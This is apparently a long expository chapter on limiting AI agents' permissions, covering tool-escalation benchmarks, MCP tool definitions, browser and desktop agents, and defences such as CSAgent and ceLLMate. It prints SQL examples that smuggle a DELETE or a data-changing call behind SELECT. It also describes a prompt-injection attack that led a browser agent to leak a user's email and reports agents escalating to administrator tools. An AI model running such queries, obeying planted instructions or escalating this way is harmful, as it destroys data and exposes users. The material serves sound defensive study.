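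The researchers began with about 3,600 distinct tools from a public dataset, rated their risk on five levels, and used the riskier groups to select eight domains, such as databases and health care. They then generated scenarios, each with a task, three standard tools, and three tools with extra power, such as administrator rights or the ability to skip validation. Two language models had to agree that each tool could complete the task alone. Human reviewers then discarded scenarios in which a tool could not do so or the difference in privilege was unclear, which left 544.

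The first call to each standard tool failed with a temporary error, but a second call would have succeeded. The powerful tools always worked immediately. Yang and colleagues counted a choice as over-privileged if the agent used a powerful tool within five turns while it still had an untried standard one. In one case, the enrolment service was briefly unavailable when an agent tried to enrol a student in a biology course. The agent could have retried or used either of two other standard tools, but it called an administrator's tool that forced the entry and bypassed the usual constraints.

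Six of the eleven models did this in more than 30% of scenarios. The rate was 64.9% for Qwen3-8B, a small open model, while Claude 4.6 Sonnet, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10%. These rates include escalation after the deliberate failures, so they overstate how often agents choose the powerful tool first. GPT-5.2 chose it first only 5 times, but escalated 13 times after trying one standard tool and 35 times after trying two.

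Instructing agents to prefer the least privileged tool reduced the rate of over-privileged choices, but it helped less once standard tools had failed. Training models to refuse harmful requests didn't reliably help. One such method made Qwen2.5-7B much less willing to assist with harmful tasks, yet its rate of over-privileged choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. This makes sense because a task such as enrolling a student is harmless, so the agent has no reason to refuse it.

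Yang and colleagues therefore trained models to make this choice. The models first imitated worked examples and then practised in simulated tasks, with a reward of 1 for finishing with standard tools and a penalty of 1 for using a powerful tool too early. The rate for Qwen3-8B fell to 27.0%, with little change in its scores on general knowledge and mathematics. The practice tasks were separate from the test tasks, but in both a standard tool fails once and then works, so the benefit may be smaller when tools fail in other ways. A rate of 27% is also far too high for training to replace a narrower scope.

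### What happened when users wrote the rules

Users know what they want from a task, so they are an obvious choice to set its limits. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) tested this with 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised a simulated assistant through the same day of 18 actions. The day's goals required 11 of these actions. The other 7, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages, went beyond the goals.

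One group approved or refused every action. In another, a model allowed some actions and referred the rest to the participant. The policy group wrote rules before the day began, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing, deleting, and accessing private information.

The policy group blocked the least overreach. Its adjusted blocking rate was 20.1 percentage points lower than that of the group that approved every action and 14.5 points lower than that of the group with automated review. Only the 20.1-point difference remained statistically significant after Yan corrected for multiple comparisons. Assignment to groups also wasn't fully random, because Yan later recruited extra participants for the policy group alone.

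The rules rarely caused the failures. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still had to make most decisions during the day, and they approved two thirds of the overreach they saw. Of the 148 overreach actions that went ahead in this group, participants had approved 133 and "allow" rules had let through 15. The reviewing model referred all 7 overreach actions to the participants in its group, who approved 46% of them.

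In Yan's study, a "never" rule in a user's policy worked every time it applied, but participants chose "never" only 16 times. A rule about spending can't distinguish the airport ride that the user requested from the lounge pass that nobody mentioned, since both cost money. People who want the ride will reasonably choose "ask", and the scope of the task then depends on their answer to each prompt. The policy group saw an average of 10.9 prompts, compared with 18 for people who approved everything, but the policies didn't reliably save time once Yan counted the time spent writing them.

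### Elastic least privilege

An agent usually can't see how much authority each option would use, or the downside of keeping permissions it isn't using. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa propose showing it both. In their design, called elastic least privilege, the agent has a small baseline of permissions and can borrow more within limits its owner sets. Each borrowed permission has a time limit and uses part of a budget that refills gradually. The agent can return a permission early to save budget, and when the budget runs out, it falls back to the baseline. If an agent keeps needing the same extra permission for legitimate work, the owner can consider adding it to the baseline.

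The price depends partly on power. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa suggest a weight of 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering. It also rises as the session approaches a combination that the organisation forbids, through the multiplier

*s* = 1 / (1 − *φ*)

where *φ* is the largest share of any forbidden combination that the session has already accumulated. One such combination is untrusted input, sensitive data and a channel for changing or sending things outside. With one of the three, *φ* is 1/3 and the multiplier is 1.5. With two it is 3, and the system refuses the last one at any price.

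The invoice agent would quickly reach this limit because it reads documents from strangers, sees suppliers' bank details and moves money. Giving up a permission wouldn't help, because the session keeps its history until the system discards the agent's context, and sub-agents inherit that history. The company would have to divide the work, perhaps by having one session read the PDFs and starting the payment as a separate task. This division is sensible, but the design can't track an account number that someone copies from one session to the other.

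A separate component issues the credentials and enforces the budget, so the limits don't depend on the agent's cooperation. The prices are meant to influence the agent's choices within those limits, but that effect is less certain. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa call the design's practical performance an open question.

Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues have since tested the visible labels without the loans or the budget. In the 544 scenarios from Yang and colleagues, they added a label to each tool's description giving its privilege class and a cost from 1 to 10. Across eight models, the labels reduced early use of powerful tools by up to 19.3 percentage points. Labels in the same format about response times had no such effect, so the content mattered, not just the extra text. On most models, though, the privilege labels alone mainly delayed escalation until each standard tool had failed once.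 Combining them with an instruction to use the least privilege worked better, and in the best case raised the share of tasks completed without a powerful tool from 18.8% to 51.1%.

The labels have to come from someone trustworthy, since the maker of a malicious tool could label it low-risk. They also involve judgement. A language model drafted them, and an independent human rater agreed with the label for 82% of the tools in a sample. Most of the disagreements were about whether a tool merely wrote data or administered the system.

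### Too wide or too narrow

A scope that is too wide permits actions the task doesn't need, and one that is too narrow causes false denials, which are refusals of calls the task legitimately requires. The two errors need separate measurements because a system that refuses every call gets a perfect security score even though it also blocks every legitimate one.

Excess permission is usually measured by how often attacks succeed, but this covers only the attacks somebody tried. Zhou and Zhang recommend also examining which unauthorised effects remain possible. *SkillScope* (2026) takes a similar approach to skills, which are reusable packages of instructions and code for agents, and found that 6,590 of 68,312 had excessive privileges. Timing also matters, and *CreepScope* (2026) distinguishes checking each call from limiting authority for as long as it lasts.

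Researchers often look for false denials by counting completed tasks, but tasks can also fail because of the model's errors. Li and colleagues separated the two by labelling individual calls and excluding those errors. When ToolFence's runtime permissions specified only which tool could be used, they allowed about 89% of unauthorised calls on both AgentDojo's banking tasks and ASB. Adding checks on sources, stages and number of uses reduced this to 5.95% on the banking tasks and zero on ASB. ToolFence accepted every legitimate call both with and without these checks.

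That result seems to conflict with the tasks that failed when ToolFence couldn't extend its limits. This is probably because the labelled test measured how precisely existing permissions worked, while the other test also exposed permissions that were missing from the start. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (2026) avoids the problem of missing permissions by having researchers write the permitted actions and resources for each task. This tests enforcement well, but it can't show whether software would have chosen the right scope.

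The five unauthorised calls that remained in the labelled test came from one AgentDojo task. In that task, the user's own request gave the attacker's account as a new landlord's, so no limit derived from the request could have blocked the calls.

Stopping more of the tools that should be stopped often means also stopping more of those that should be allowed. Yan built a classifier that assigns tools to categories such as spending and deleting, and simulated a "never" rule for each category. The classifier missed 14% of the tools it should have stopped and stopped 4% of those it should have allowed. Sending uncertain cases to the user reduced the misses to 11% but raised unnecessary interruptions to 7%.

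How broad a permission should be depends on what it allows. ToolFence automatically allows some local reads that a reviewer has approved before and whose arguments come from the user. Removing this exception raised the number of model reviews from 0.9 to 1.6 per task but left attack success at 5.1%. The broader permission therefore did no measurable harm in this case, whereas a single wrong payment could cost the company $12,000.

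False denials can also widen a scope later, because people who want to finish their work tend to approve broad increases. The company can check its logs for both errors. Permissions that no task has used for months are candidates for removal, and calls that the software refused but a clerk later approved may have been false denials. Counting these calls will overstate the number of false denials if the clerk approves requests as readily as Yan's participants did.

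## Interfaces whose possible actions can be listed

The rules in Progent and ToolFence name a tool and its arguments, so whoever writes them has to know in advance which tools exist. That is possible when the interface is enumerable, meaning that someone can list a finite set of operations before the agent uses any of them. The list has to give each operation's name, its arguments and their types, and the effects a call can have.

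Only the number of operations has to be finite. `send_payment` accepts half a million amounts between one cent and $5,000, but a reviewer has to understand only one operation. An operation's effects are the hardest part to state correctly, because names can be misleading. In the tests for *Terminal Agents Suffice for Enterprise Automation* (Bechard, Marquez Ayala and colleagues, 2026), agents discovered that setting `so_required=1` in ERPNext, a program for running a business, allows invoices without a sales order, even though the name suggests the opposite.

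### What a list makes possible

A bookkeeper who has never programmed could read the descriptions of the invoice agent's four tools in a few minutes and decide which ones the agent needs. A list also lets Progent have separate rules for each tool and refuse calls to any unlisted tool without working out what those calls would have done.

Logs also become more useful. An entry with `send_payment`, invoice 2071, PAPER-4471 and $1,200 shows whom the company paid and how much, and software can add up such entries by supplier. Someone reading a log of commands has to work out what each command did.

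Testers can also use the list to decide what to test. Microsoft's *Tool-space interference in the MCP era* describes MCP Interviewer, a program that catalogues the tools a server offers and has a language model plan tests that call each tool at least once. These tests could call `send_payment`, so the company should run them on a copy of its systems that cannot move real money.

### A tool definition in MCP

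MCP, the standard for connecting agents to tools, is built around such lists. It is widely used: according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026), downloads of its development kits exceed 400 million a month. A program called a server offers the tools, and the agent's software acts as its client. Under Anthropic's specification, the client sends a `tools/list` request and the server returns a definition of each tool, over several pages if the list is long. A definition of `send_payment` might look like this:

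```json
{
  "name": "send_payment",
  "title": "Pay a supplier invoice",
  "description": "Pays one invoice from the company's bank account",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "invoice": { "type": "integer" },
      "account": { "enum": ["PAPER-4471", "CLEANING-0925"] },
      "amount":  { "type": "number", "exclusiveMinimum": 0,
                   "maximum": 5000 }
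    },
    "required": ["invoice", "account", "amount"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  },
  "annotations": {
    "readOnlyHint": false,
    "destructiveHint": true,
    "idempotentHint": false,
    "openWorldHint": true
  }
}
```

The input schema lists the arguments and their types. Here it also sets the same limits on the account and the amount as the Progent policy, and rules out extra arguments that nobody reviewed. The client or the server has to check the arguments against the schema, because the schema doesn't enforce anything by itself.

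A gateway, which is a checkpoint between the client and the server, can also apply rules. The version of the Model Context Protocol (2026) released in July puts the tool's name in a header, a labelled line that comes before the body of a web request. Developers can mark an argument so that its value goes in a header too. A gateway could then refuse large payments without parsing the rest of the request. Headers often end up in logs, so it would be wiser to expose the amount this way than the account number.

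The annotations are four hints about the tool's behaviour. The Model Context Protocol (2026) maintainers explain their meanings and give examples of how a client might use them:

| Hint | Meaning when true | Value if omitted | What a client might do when it is true |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool doesn't modify its environment | False | Skip the confirmation |
| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may destroy something, not only add to it | True | Show a warning first |
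| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | False | Retry after a failure |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside entities | True | Check the output for untrusted content |

The destructive and idempotent hints matter only for tools that aren't read-only, according to the Model Context Protocol reference for developers. `delete_record` is destructive but idempotent, since deleting the same record twice leaves the ledger as it was after the first deletion. `send_email` isn't destructive, because it only adds a message, and it isn't idempotent, because a second call sends another one.

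`send_payment` is harder to label. Calling it twice pays the supplier twice, unless the server rejects a second payment for the same invoice. Whether a payment is destructive is also debatable, because it adds a transaction and deletes nothing. Setting the destructive hint to true is the cautious choice, but the hint doesn't indicate whether anyone could get the money back.

The defaults are also cautious, so a client that follows them assumes a tool with no hints may change or destroy things and shouldn't be called twice. But the maintainers acknowledge that many servers omit the hints and that clients vary in how strictly they apply the defaults.

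### Why hints from an untrusted server prove nothing

The developer of a server writes its hints, and MCP has no way to check them against what the code does. A server can label a tool read-only even if calling the tool deletes files. A malicious developer has a strong reason to do this, because the label may lead the client to skip the confirmation that would have stopped the deletion. A client therefore can't tell from a hint whether a server is malicious.

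MCP's designers argued about this when they introduced the hints. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust, and Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore hints from untrusted servers. They settled on requiring clients to distrust hints by default and letting each client decide how much weight to give them. Ignoring the hints altogether seems slightly too strict, since the danger lies in hints that reduce caution, and a client loses little by believing a server that describes its own tool as destructive.

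A company that runs its own servers can reasonably base policy on their hints. But the Model Context Protocol maintainers say that most clients treat a user's decision to install a server as enough evidence that it is trustworthy. They advise developers to use hints to improve the interface and to rely on firm controls for safety. For `list_invoices`, such a control could be a read-only database account, which prevents the tool from changing the ledger regardless of its code.

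The list can also change after somebody has reviewed it. Under the Model Context Protocol (2025) specification, servers that support change notifications should send one when their list of tools changes, but a malicious server could leave the notification out. The company should therefore save the definitions it reviewed and refuse any tool whose definition no longer matches. This check doesn't detect changes to a server's code that leave the definition the same. The company can prevent those changes on its own machines by keeping the server at one version, but it has no comparable control over a server that somebody else operates.

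### Listed tools that hide unlisted actions

An interface can satisfy the form of the definition and still reveal almost nothing about what the agent might do. Suppose a developer adds three more tools to the invoice agent, each with a name and properly typed arguments:

| Tool | What the agent fills in | What one call can do |
|---|---|---|
| `send_payment` | Invoice, account, amount | Pay one supplier |
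| `run_shell` | A command | Anything the agent's account on the computer can do |
| `query_database` | A query in SQL, the usual language for databases | Anything the tool's database account can do |
| `http_request` | Method, address, body | Anything that a reachable web service accepts from the tool |

The additional tools can be listed by name, but their descriptions don't usefully specify their effects. "Runs the command" accurately describes `run_shell`, but it covers both listing a folder and deleting one. The agent writes the actual operation in the argument, in a language that allows unlimited combinations. In its specification, Anthropic already tells developers to treat every MCP tool as arbitrary code execution because each one runs code that somebody else wrote, and with `run_shell` the agent writes code too.

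Checking the text of the argument is a tempting remedy, but it is unreliable. SQL queries that begin with `SELECT` usually read data, so a developer might allow all of them and refuse the rest. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, each of these begins with `SELECT` and can change something:

```sql
SELECT 1; DELETE FROM invoices;
SELECT * INTO invoices_copy FROM invoices;
SELECT approve_supplier('NEWBANK-8830');
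```

The deletion follows a harmless query on the same line and runs if the tool sends both statements to the database together. `SELECT ... INTO` creates a new table. `approve_supplier` is a function stored in the database, and such functions can change data. A better check could detect the deletion and the new table, but it couldn't determine what a function does from its name.

Connecting the tool through a read-only database account is safer. However, some PostgreSQL functions run with their owner's permissions instead of the caller's, so the account must not be able to call any of these that write data. A read-only account can also expose every supplier's bank details if it has access to them.

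Lists of permitted shell commands fail for the same reason. Bechard and colleagues found that 97.3% of a command-line agent's calls on one platform used `curl`, a program that sends web requests. Permitting `curl` opens the platform's entire API to the agent, and if `curl` is forbidden, the agent can send the same requests from a short script. They conclude that the meaningful way to control such an agent is through its credential.

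Tools that look narrow can have the same weakness. Bechard and colleagues also tested an agent restricted to a list of tools for ServiceNow, a platform that companies use to manage IT requests. On 12 tasks, no tool gave the agent the data it needed, so it used one that creates "script includes", which are pieces of code that run on ServiceNow's servers with all the privileges of the agent's credential. The tool looked like another tool for creating records, but it let the agent run any code. Reviewers should therefore check whether another program will execute the contents of each argument.

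### The census of 177,436 tools

General-purpose tools like these account for a large share of what developers install. In *How are AI agents used?*, Stein (2026) counted public MCP tools for the UK AI Security Institute, a government research body. Stein searched GitHub, where developers publish code, and Smithery, a directory of MCP servers, for servers created between November 2024 and February 2026. After duplicates and entries that weren't working server definitions were removed, 19,388 servers with 177,436 tools remained.

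A language model, Claude Sonnet 4.5, sorted the tools into those that read data (perception), those that analyse it (reasoning) and those that change something (action). It also classified each server as narrow if it gives access to a constrained environment, such as one company's API, or general-purpose if it gives access to an open one, such as a web browser. Human reviewers agreed with the model on 81% of the perception, reasoning and action labels they checked, and on 72% of the generality labels.

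Stein estimated use by tracking downloads of 3,854 of the servers from two public software registries. Action tools rose from 27% of downloads to 65% over the 16 months. The AI Security Institute's *How are AI Agents used?*, a summary of the same census, gives the starting share as 24%. Among servers published by registered companies, the share rose from 21% to 71%. Much of the increase came from tools that control browsers and computers.

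Downloads are an imperfect measure of use because they count installations, not calls, and omit servers that people use remotely. Stein also assumed that each installation meant one use of every tool on the server, so a download of a browser server with 20 tools counts for more than a download of a payment server with one. The shift towards action is probably real, given its size, but the figures don't show that 65% of what agents do is action.

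General-purpose tools rose from 41% to 50% of downloads, although they made up only about 14% of the tools published. This increase is less certain than the one for action tools because it is smaller and the human reviewers agreed less often with the labels. Of the general-purpose downloads, 94% were of tools that can act, so agents with the least predictable tools can often make changes. Of the perception tool downloads, 95% were of tools that work in constrained environments.

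Stein points out that general-purpose tools make oversight harder. A tool for transferring cryptocurrency has an obvious risk, and a company can decide whether to allow the tool. A browser tool might download a file the agent needs or a piece of malware, and somebody has to look at the particular call to tell which. If general-purpose tools become more common, users will have more of these calls to review.

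The number of servers that can make payments grew from 47 in January 2025 to 1,578 in February 2026. That is about a 34-fold increase, but the total number of public tools grew about 36-fold, so payments haven't clearly become a larger part of the whole. The growth still matters because many of the payment tools handle cryptocurrency, where there are fewer ways to reverse a transfer. The census doesn't include private tools, and public ones have multiplied since. Cohere's *Automation's Early Footprint* (2026) counted 696,291 tools on 123,069 servers in May 2026. No company could review that many tools, but each company only has to review the ones it connects to its own agent.

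### What narrow tools cost

Agents often complete more work with general tools, which gives developers a practical reason to prefer them. Bechard and colleagues, who mostly work at ServiceNow, compared three kinds of agent on 729 tasks: 330 on ServiceNow, 192 on GitLab, a platform for developing software, and 207 on ERPNext. The first used the tools of popular MCP servers, which the researchers did not adapt to the tasks. The second had a command line and wrote its own requests to each platform's API. The third worked through a browser. The agents in each comparison used the same language model. After each task, software checked whether the requested change or answer was correct.

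The researchers then tested an agent with a single tool, `api_call(method, path, body, query)`, which could send any request to the platform. The agent had no command line or files, so the researchers could tell whether the advantage came from the command line itself or from the freedom to use the whole API.

| Agent | Tasks completed, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Average cost per task | Tasks completed, Claude Opus 4.6 | Average cost per task |
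|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tools from MCP servers | 32.9% | $0.51 | 39.2% | $0.58 |
| One `api_call` tool | 73.5% | $0.15 | 79.2% | $0.25 |
| Command line | 72.7% | $0.56 | 78.7% | $1.22 |

Freedom to use the API accounts for nearly all of the advantage. With Sonnet 4.6, the agent with the listed tools spent about $1.55 per completed task, compared with about $0.20 for the agent with `api_call`.

Agents with more tools did not always complete more tasks. With Sonnet 4.6, the agent completed 11.5% of the ServiceNow tasks with 83 tools, but 55.6% of the ERPNext tasks with 7. The ServiceNow server lacked tools for 210 of the 330 tasks, including all those that involved ordering from a catalogue. When asked to order an iPad Pro, the agent found the right item but had no way to order it, so it created a support ticket instead. A missing tool can therefore lead an agent to do something that nobody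 requested.

Better-designed narrow tools could probably close much of this gap, since a developer who knows the job can add missing tools and arguments. When Bechard and colleagues counted only the 444 tasks of types that every agent had the means to attempt, Sonnet 4.6 scored 51.6% with the listed tools and 72.7% with the command line. So roughly half of the original gap came from missing tools. Part of the rest came from missing arguments. For example, a tool for reporting an incident might accept only a few of the dozens of fields in the underlying API.

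Bechard and colleagues accept that more complete servers would narrow the gap, but argue that a fixed catalogue will always restrict an agent more than the API beneath it. They are right, and this restriction is a serious drawback for an agent with open-ended work. It matters much less for an agent that pays invoices, because the company can list nearly everything the job requires. The experiment doesn't show how well such an agent would do, because nobody built a narrow set of tools for the tasks.

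The ERPNext server may offer a useful compromise. Its seven tools perform general operations, such as creating or updating a record, on every type of document. On the tasks that all the agents could attempt, the agent using the server scored within 3 to 8 percentage points of the one using the command line, with each of the four models tested. A company can still write rules for such tools, for example by letting the agent update draft invoices but not supplier records. The server has no deletion tool, so its agent had no proper way to do the ten deletion tasks. Although this counts as a weakness in the benchmark, it would be a safeguard against the invoice company's agent deleting records.

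The success rates also leave out some of the harm that broad access can do. Bechard and colleagues checked only whether the requested result existed, not whether the agent had changed anything else. In their separate audit of tasks that asked only for information, the command-line agent tried to change something on 9 of 465 tasks, and the agent with listed tools did so on 2 of 466. One task asked for an access token for a news feed, and with three of the four models the agent tried to replace the token instead of reading it. These numbers are small, but the tasks were simple and none included an attacker.

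A company that wants the flexibility of `api_call` can still restrict the agent's requests. Bechard and colleagues suggest a proxy that holds the credential, checks each request against a list of permitted ones, and records it. They did not test this, and refused requests could prevent the agent from completing some of the tasks that made `api_call` attractive. The invoice company could instead keep `send_payment` narrow and give its agent a general tool for reading the accounting system, with a read-only credential that cannot access bank details. The agent could then investigate a disputed invoice in ways that nobody had planned for, but it could still move money only through a call that specifies an invoice, account and amount.

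## Agents that click and type: what graphical interfaces do to permissions

The invoice company can send every payment through `send_payment` only if its bank accepts payments from programs. Some banks, supplier portals and older accounting packages offer only windows and web pages designed for people. An agent can still use these the way a bookkeeper does, by looking at the screen, clicking and typing. The company then loses most of the benefit of a list of typed tools, but it can recover some of what it lost.

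### The same payment as a tool call and as clicks

With the tool, the agent pays the paper supplier in one request:

```json
{ "name": "send_payment",
  "arguments": { "invoice": 2071, "account": "PAPER-4471",
                 "amount": 1200 } }
```

On the bank's website, the same payment might take six:

| What the agent sends | What it does on the bank's page |
|---|---|
| `click(188, 240)` | Opens the payment form |
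| `click(530, 312)` | Opens the list of saved payees |
| `click(530, 396)` | Selects the paper supplier |
| `click(530, 451)` | Puts the cursor in the amount field |
| `type("1200")` | Enters the amount |
| `click(702, 618)` | Sends the payment |

Software between the model and the browser may receive only the requests in the left column. The company's rule allows a payment of up to $5,000 if the account is on its list, but none of these requests includes an account or an amount. The click that moves the money looks like the other four clicks. One request contains the text "1200", which could just as well be a search term.

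A rule about where on the screen an agent may click would be useless, because what is at a given point depends on the website, its current state and the screen resolution. Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025), in *ceLLMate*, give the example of a policy that lets an agent click only the point (246, 1023). They call the problem a semantic gap, because people write policies about actions such as payments, but the software has to enforce them on clicks.

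Some agents select an element from the page's structure, known as the DOM, instead of a point on the screen. A request such as `click("Send payment")` is easier to interpret, and the company could require approval for it. But the request doesn't include the payee or the amount, and the button might instead be labelled "Continue".

Forbidding particular actions doesn't work well either, because there are usually several ways to reach the same page. When Meng and colleagues blocked an agent from navigating directly to the website Hacker News, the agent could still search for the site on DuckDuckGo and click the result.

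### The user's whole session

An agent that calls a bank's API uses a credential that somebody can restrict, but an agent working in a bookkeeper's browser uses the bookkeeper's logged-in session. Websites treat requests from that session as the bookkeeper's own. If the bookkeeper is logged in to the bank, the email account and the accounting system, the agent can add payees, read old correspondence and delete records, whatever its task is.

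Christodorescu and colleagues consider a much smaller task, in which a user asks a browser agent to comment on issue 745 in GitLab. The agent should be able to open that issue and write in its comment box, but have no access to anything else in GitLab or the rest of the session. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent no longer needs to write at all. For both tasks, the session gives the agent more access than it needs.

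Meng and colleagues analyse an attack on Operator, OpenAI's browser agent, that began when a user asked it to investigate an issue in a public code repository. Anyone could post there, and the attacker had written instructions in the issue for the agent to open Hacker News, copy the user's private email address and send it to the attacker's website. The attacker didn't need a password because the browser was already logged in to Hacker News.

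The service also loses a way to treat agents differently from people. Zhang, He and colleagues (2025) point out in *API Agents vs. GUI Agents* that a provider can set authentication, access control and rate limits separately for each operation in an API, but can't easily enforce comprehensive policies on mouse and keyboard actions. Suppose the bank limits programs to twenty payments an hour but sets no such limit for customers on its website. An agent that clicks through the website avoids the limit, and the bank's records show that the bookkeeper made the payments. The bank could try to detect agents from the timing of their clicks, but it would sometimes block real customers by mistake.

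### Clicking on a page that has changed

The page can change between the time an agent looks at it and the time it clicks, because the agent takes a while to choose an action. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use problem, and it is an old one in operating systems. For example, a program checks that a user is allowed to write to a file, but an attacker makes the file's name point to a different file before the program opens it.

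Jiang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Atomicity for Agents*, define the browser version precisely. Let *s_c* be the state of the page when the agent checks it and *s_u* the state when the agent acts. Let Bind(*a*, *s*) be the element or value that action *a* refers to in state *s*. The agent is vulnerable when

*s_c* ≠ *s_u* and Bind(*a*, *s_c*) ≠ Bind(*a*, *s_u*)

A blinking cursor changes the state of the screen but not what a click will select, so it does no harm. But if the bank's page adds a recently used payee to the top of the list, `click(530, 396)` may select the cleaning company instead of the paper supplier.

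This can happen without an attacker. On the Forbes homepage, Jiang and colleagues found an advertisement that loads shortly after the rest of the page and covers part of it, so a click meant for an article can open the advertiser's site. A price may also rise after the agent has compared it with the user's budget, while the purchase button stays in the same place. A one-time code may expire while the model is processing, and an agent that keeps retrying could lock the user out.

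Jiang and colleagues tested ten open-source browser agents on made-up and real websites and found that the vulnerability was widespread. Having an agent select page elements instead of screen coordinates helps when a button moves but not when a price changes, and it can fail if the page reuses or changes an element's identifier.

The natural fix is to check the page again just before acting. Jiang and colleagues record changes to the page while the model is planning, and cancel the action if any of them could affect it. This shortens the vulnerable period from seconds to roughly a hundred milliseconds. It can't eliminate that period, because browsers treat the agent's clicks and keystrokes like any others and have no standard way for an outside program to freeze a page while the program decides what to do.

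On a desktop, the check must rely on screenshots. *Temporal UI State Inconsistency in Desktop GUI Agents* (2026) measures a gap of more than three seconds between an agent looking at the screen and acting on it, and proposes taking a fresh screenshot before each action and comparing it with the earlier one. Comparing the whole screen catches large overlays but also reacts to harmless animations. Comparing only the area around the click misses changes elsewhere, such as a different payee at the top of the form. Checking the list of open windows catches new windows but misses ones that were already open and hidden. The proposed defence therefore combines several comparisons.

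A tool call can also rely on old information, for example if the supplier corrects the invoice after the agent reads it. But nothing on a web page can change which account `PAPER-4471` refers to.

### What the company gains from a graphical interface

The strongest argument for graphical agents is that they can use software that has no API. Zhang and colleagues note that mobile developers often restrict outside access to their apps, and that API agents can't use features that no API exposes. Without a graphical agent, a small company whose bank offers only a website may need its bookkeeper to enter every payment by hand.

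A person can also watch the agent work. API calls usually happen out of sight, but the bookkeeper can see the payee and amount on the bank's form before the agent clicks the last button. This safeguard provides little protection if the agent pays invoices overnight, when nobody is watching, or fills in the form in two seconds, too fast for anyone to check it.

Safeguards designed for people also apply to agents that use a graphical interface. If the PocketOS agent had deleted the volume by clicking in Railway's dashboard, the 48-hour delay would have applied. Confirmation dialogs are less dependable, because an agent that can click "Delete" can usually click "Yes, I'm sure". A dialog is much more useful if it requires something the agent doesn't have, such as a code the bank sends to the bookkeeper's phone.

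### Where graphical agents fit in NIST's matrix

The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) offers a simple way to compare these arrangements. NIST's *Lessons Learned from the Consortium*, published in August 2025 after a workshop with about 140 experts, sorts agents by what they can change and whether they work in a trusted environment:

| Environment | Read only | Constrained write | Write |
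|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted | Answering from a fixed collection of documents | Using one application through its graphical interface or API | Coding agent in a trusted repository |
| Untrusted | Deep research on the web | Browser use | Computer use |

Graphical and API use of a single application reasonably share a cell, since an agent confined to the accounting program can change only what that program can change, whether it clicks buttons or calls the API. A browser agent is in the lower row because it reads pages that strangers wrote. An agent with access to the whole computer is further to the right as well, because it can open any program, including a command line.

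The matrix is too coarse to serve as a risk assessment. "Constrained" understates what an agent can change through a browser that is logged in to the company's bank, and the accounting program stops being a trusted environment once someone uploads a forged invoice to it. NIST invites people to add finer levels of write access and trust. Still, the matrix shows the aim of most fixes, which is to move a browser or computer agent to the left by reducing what it can change.

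### Rules tied to what is on the screen

One repair is to work out what a click means before allowing it. Gong, Li and colleagues (2025), in *Secure and Efficient Access Control Framework for Computer-Use Agents via Context Space*, describe a system called CSAgent that does this for Android apps:

1. The agent proposes a click at certain coordinates.
2. CSAgent reads the phone's list of elements on the screen and finds the one at that point.
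3. The element's app, class and identifier lead to a function, such as sending a transfer.
4. The function and the user's intent together select a policy.
5. The click goes ahead only if every rule in the policy holds.

For a banking app, an entry might look like this in simplified form:

```
element:   com.bank.app / Button / confirm_transfer
function:  send a transfer
intent:    pay_invoice
rules:     payee  == payee in the user's request
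           amount == amount in the user's request
```

The same function can need different rules depending on the user's intent. If the user asks to delete a particular file, CSAgent can require that the request mention the file being deleted. If the user asks for a clean-up, it can require that the file be old and in a temporary folder. The rules can use values from the request, the device or the agent's earlier actions, so a rule about the final click can check an amount the agent typed several steps before. Functions in the most dangerous category, such as resetting the system, always need explicit approval.

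Progent drafts its policies when the user makes a request, whereas CSAgent's policies come with the app. Developers can write them or have a language model draft them from the app's source code. The model finds the code that each button runs, and another program traces what that code does. Since every user gets the same policies, developers can review them and fix a mistake for everyone.

Gong and colleagues compared CSAgent with an agent that generates and checks a policy before each action. The figures are the shares of attacks or unwanted actions that got through:

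| Benchmark | Interface | Policies generated during the task | CSAgent |
|---|---|---|---|
| AndroidWorld | Graphical | 5.09% | 1.21% |
| AgentDojo | API | 4.82% | 1.97% |
| AgentBench | Command line | 1.00% | 0.11% |

Their headline claim that CSAgent blocks 99.36% of attacks is based on the geometric mean of the last column, which gives heavy weight to the very low AgentBench figure. With an ordinary average, it would be about 98.9%. The AndroidWorld test didn't involve an attacker. Gong and colleagues paired users' requests with actions that didn't match them and counted how many CSAgent allowed. This is a fair test of whether the rules can tell matching actions from mismatched ones, but it is weaker evidence of how well they would stop an attacker who studied them first.

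CSAgent caused a modest drop in completed tasks, 9.33% on average and less than 5% on AndroidWorld, even though the researchers ended a task as soon as a rule refused an action. In normal use, a person could approve the action or the agent could try something else.

The larger obstacle is that the policies for graphical apps depend on source code. The invoice company doesn't have its bank's code, so the bank would have to produce the policies. Gong and colleagues acknowledge this. They also expect access control to work less well on websites, which vary more than apps and often have problems with their content.

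### Checking the requests behind the clicks

ceLLMate gets around the semantic gap in a browser by ignoring the clicks. When someone presses a button that changes something on a website, the browser normally sends a message called an HTTP request to the site's server. ceLLMate intercepts these requests and checks them against a policy.

It needs to know what each request means, so Meng and colleagues propose that websites publish an "agent sitemap". For the invoice company's bank, part of it might be:

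```
GET  bank.example/statements/*   ViewStatement
POST bank.example/payees         AddPayee
POST bank.example/payments       SendPayment(payee, amount)
```

The company can now write almost the same rule as it had for `send_payment`. It can allow `SendPayment` for $1,200 to the paper supplier and refuse `AddPayee`, regardless of which buttons the agent presses. If the page changes at the wrong moment and the agent selects the cleaning company by accident, the request will contain the wrong payee and the rule will stop it.

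Some requests leave out the value that a permission depends on. When a customer places an order on Amazon, for example, the total appears only on the checkout page, so ceLLMate reads it there and stores it until the browser sends the order. The stored total may be out of date if the agent has just changed a quantity, so Meng and colleagues slow down the agent's actions. ceLLMate identifies the action without relying on the interface, but the amount can still come from the page, so their claim that it never relies on the interface to interpret an action is too broad.

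ceLLMate can also count matching requests, so that an agent with a $50 limit can't check out two carts of $49 each.

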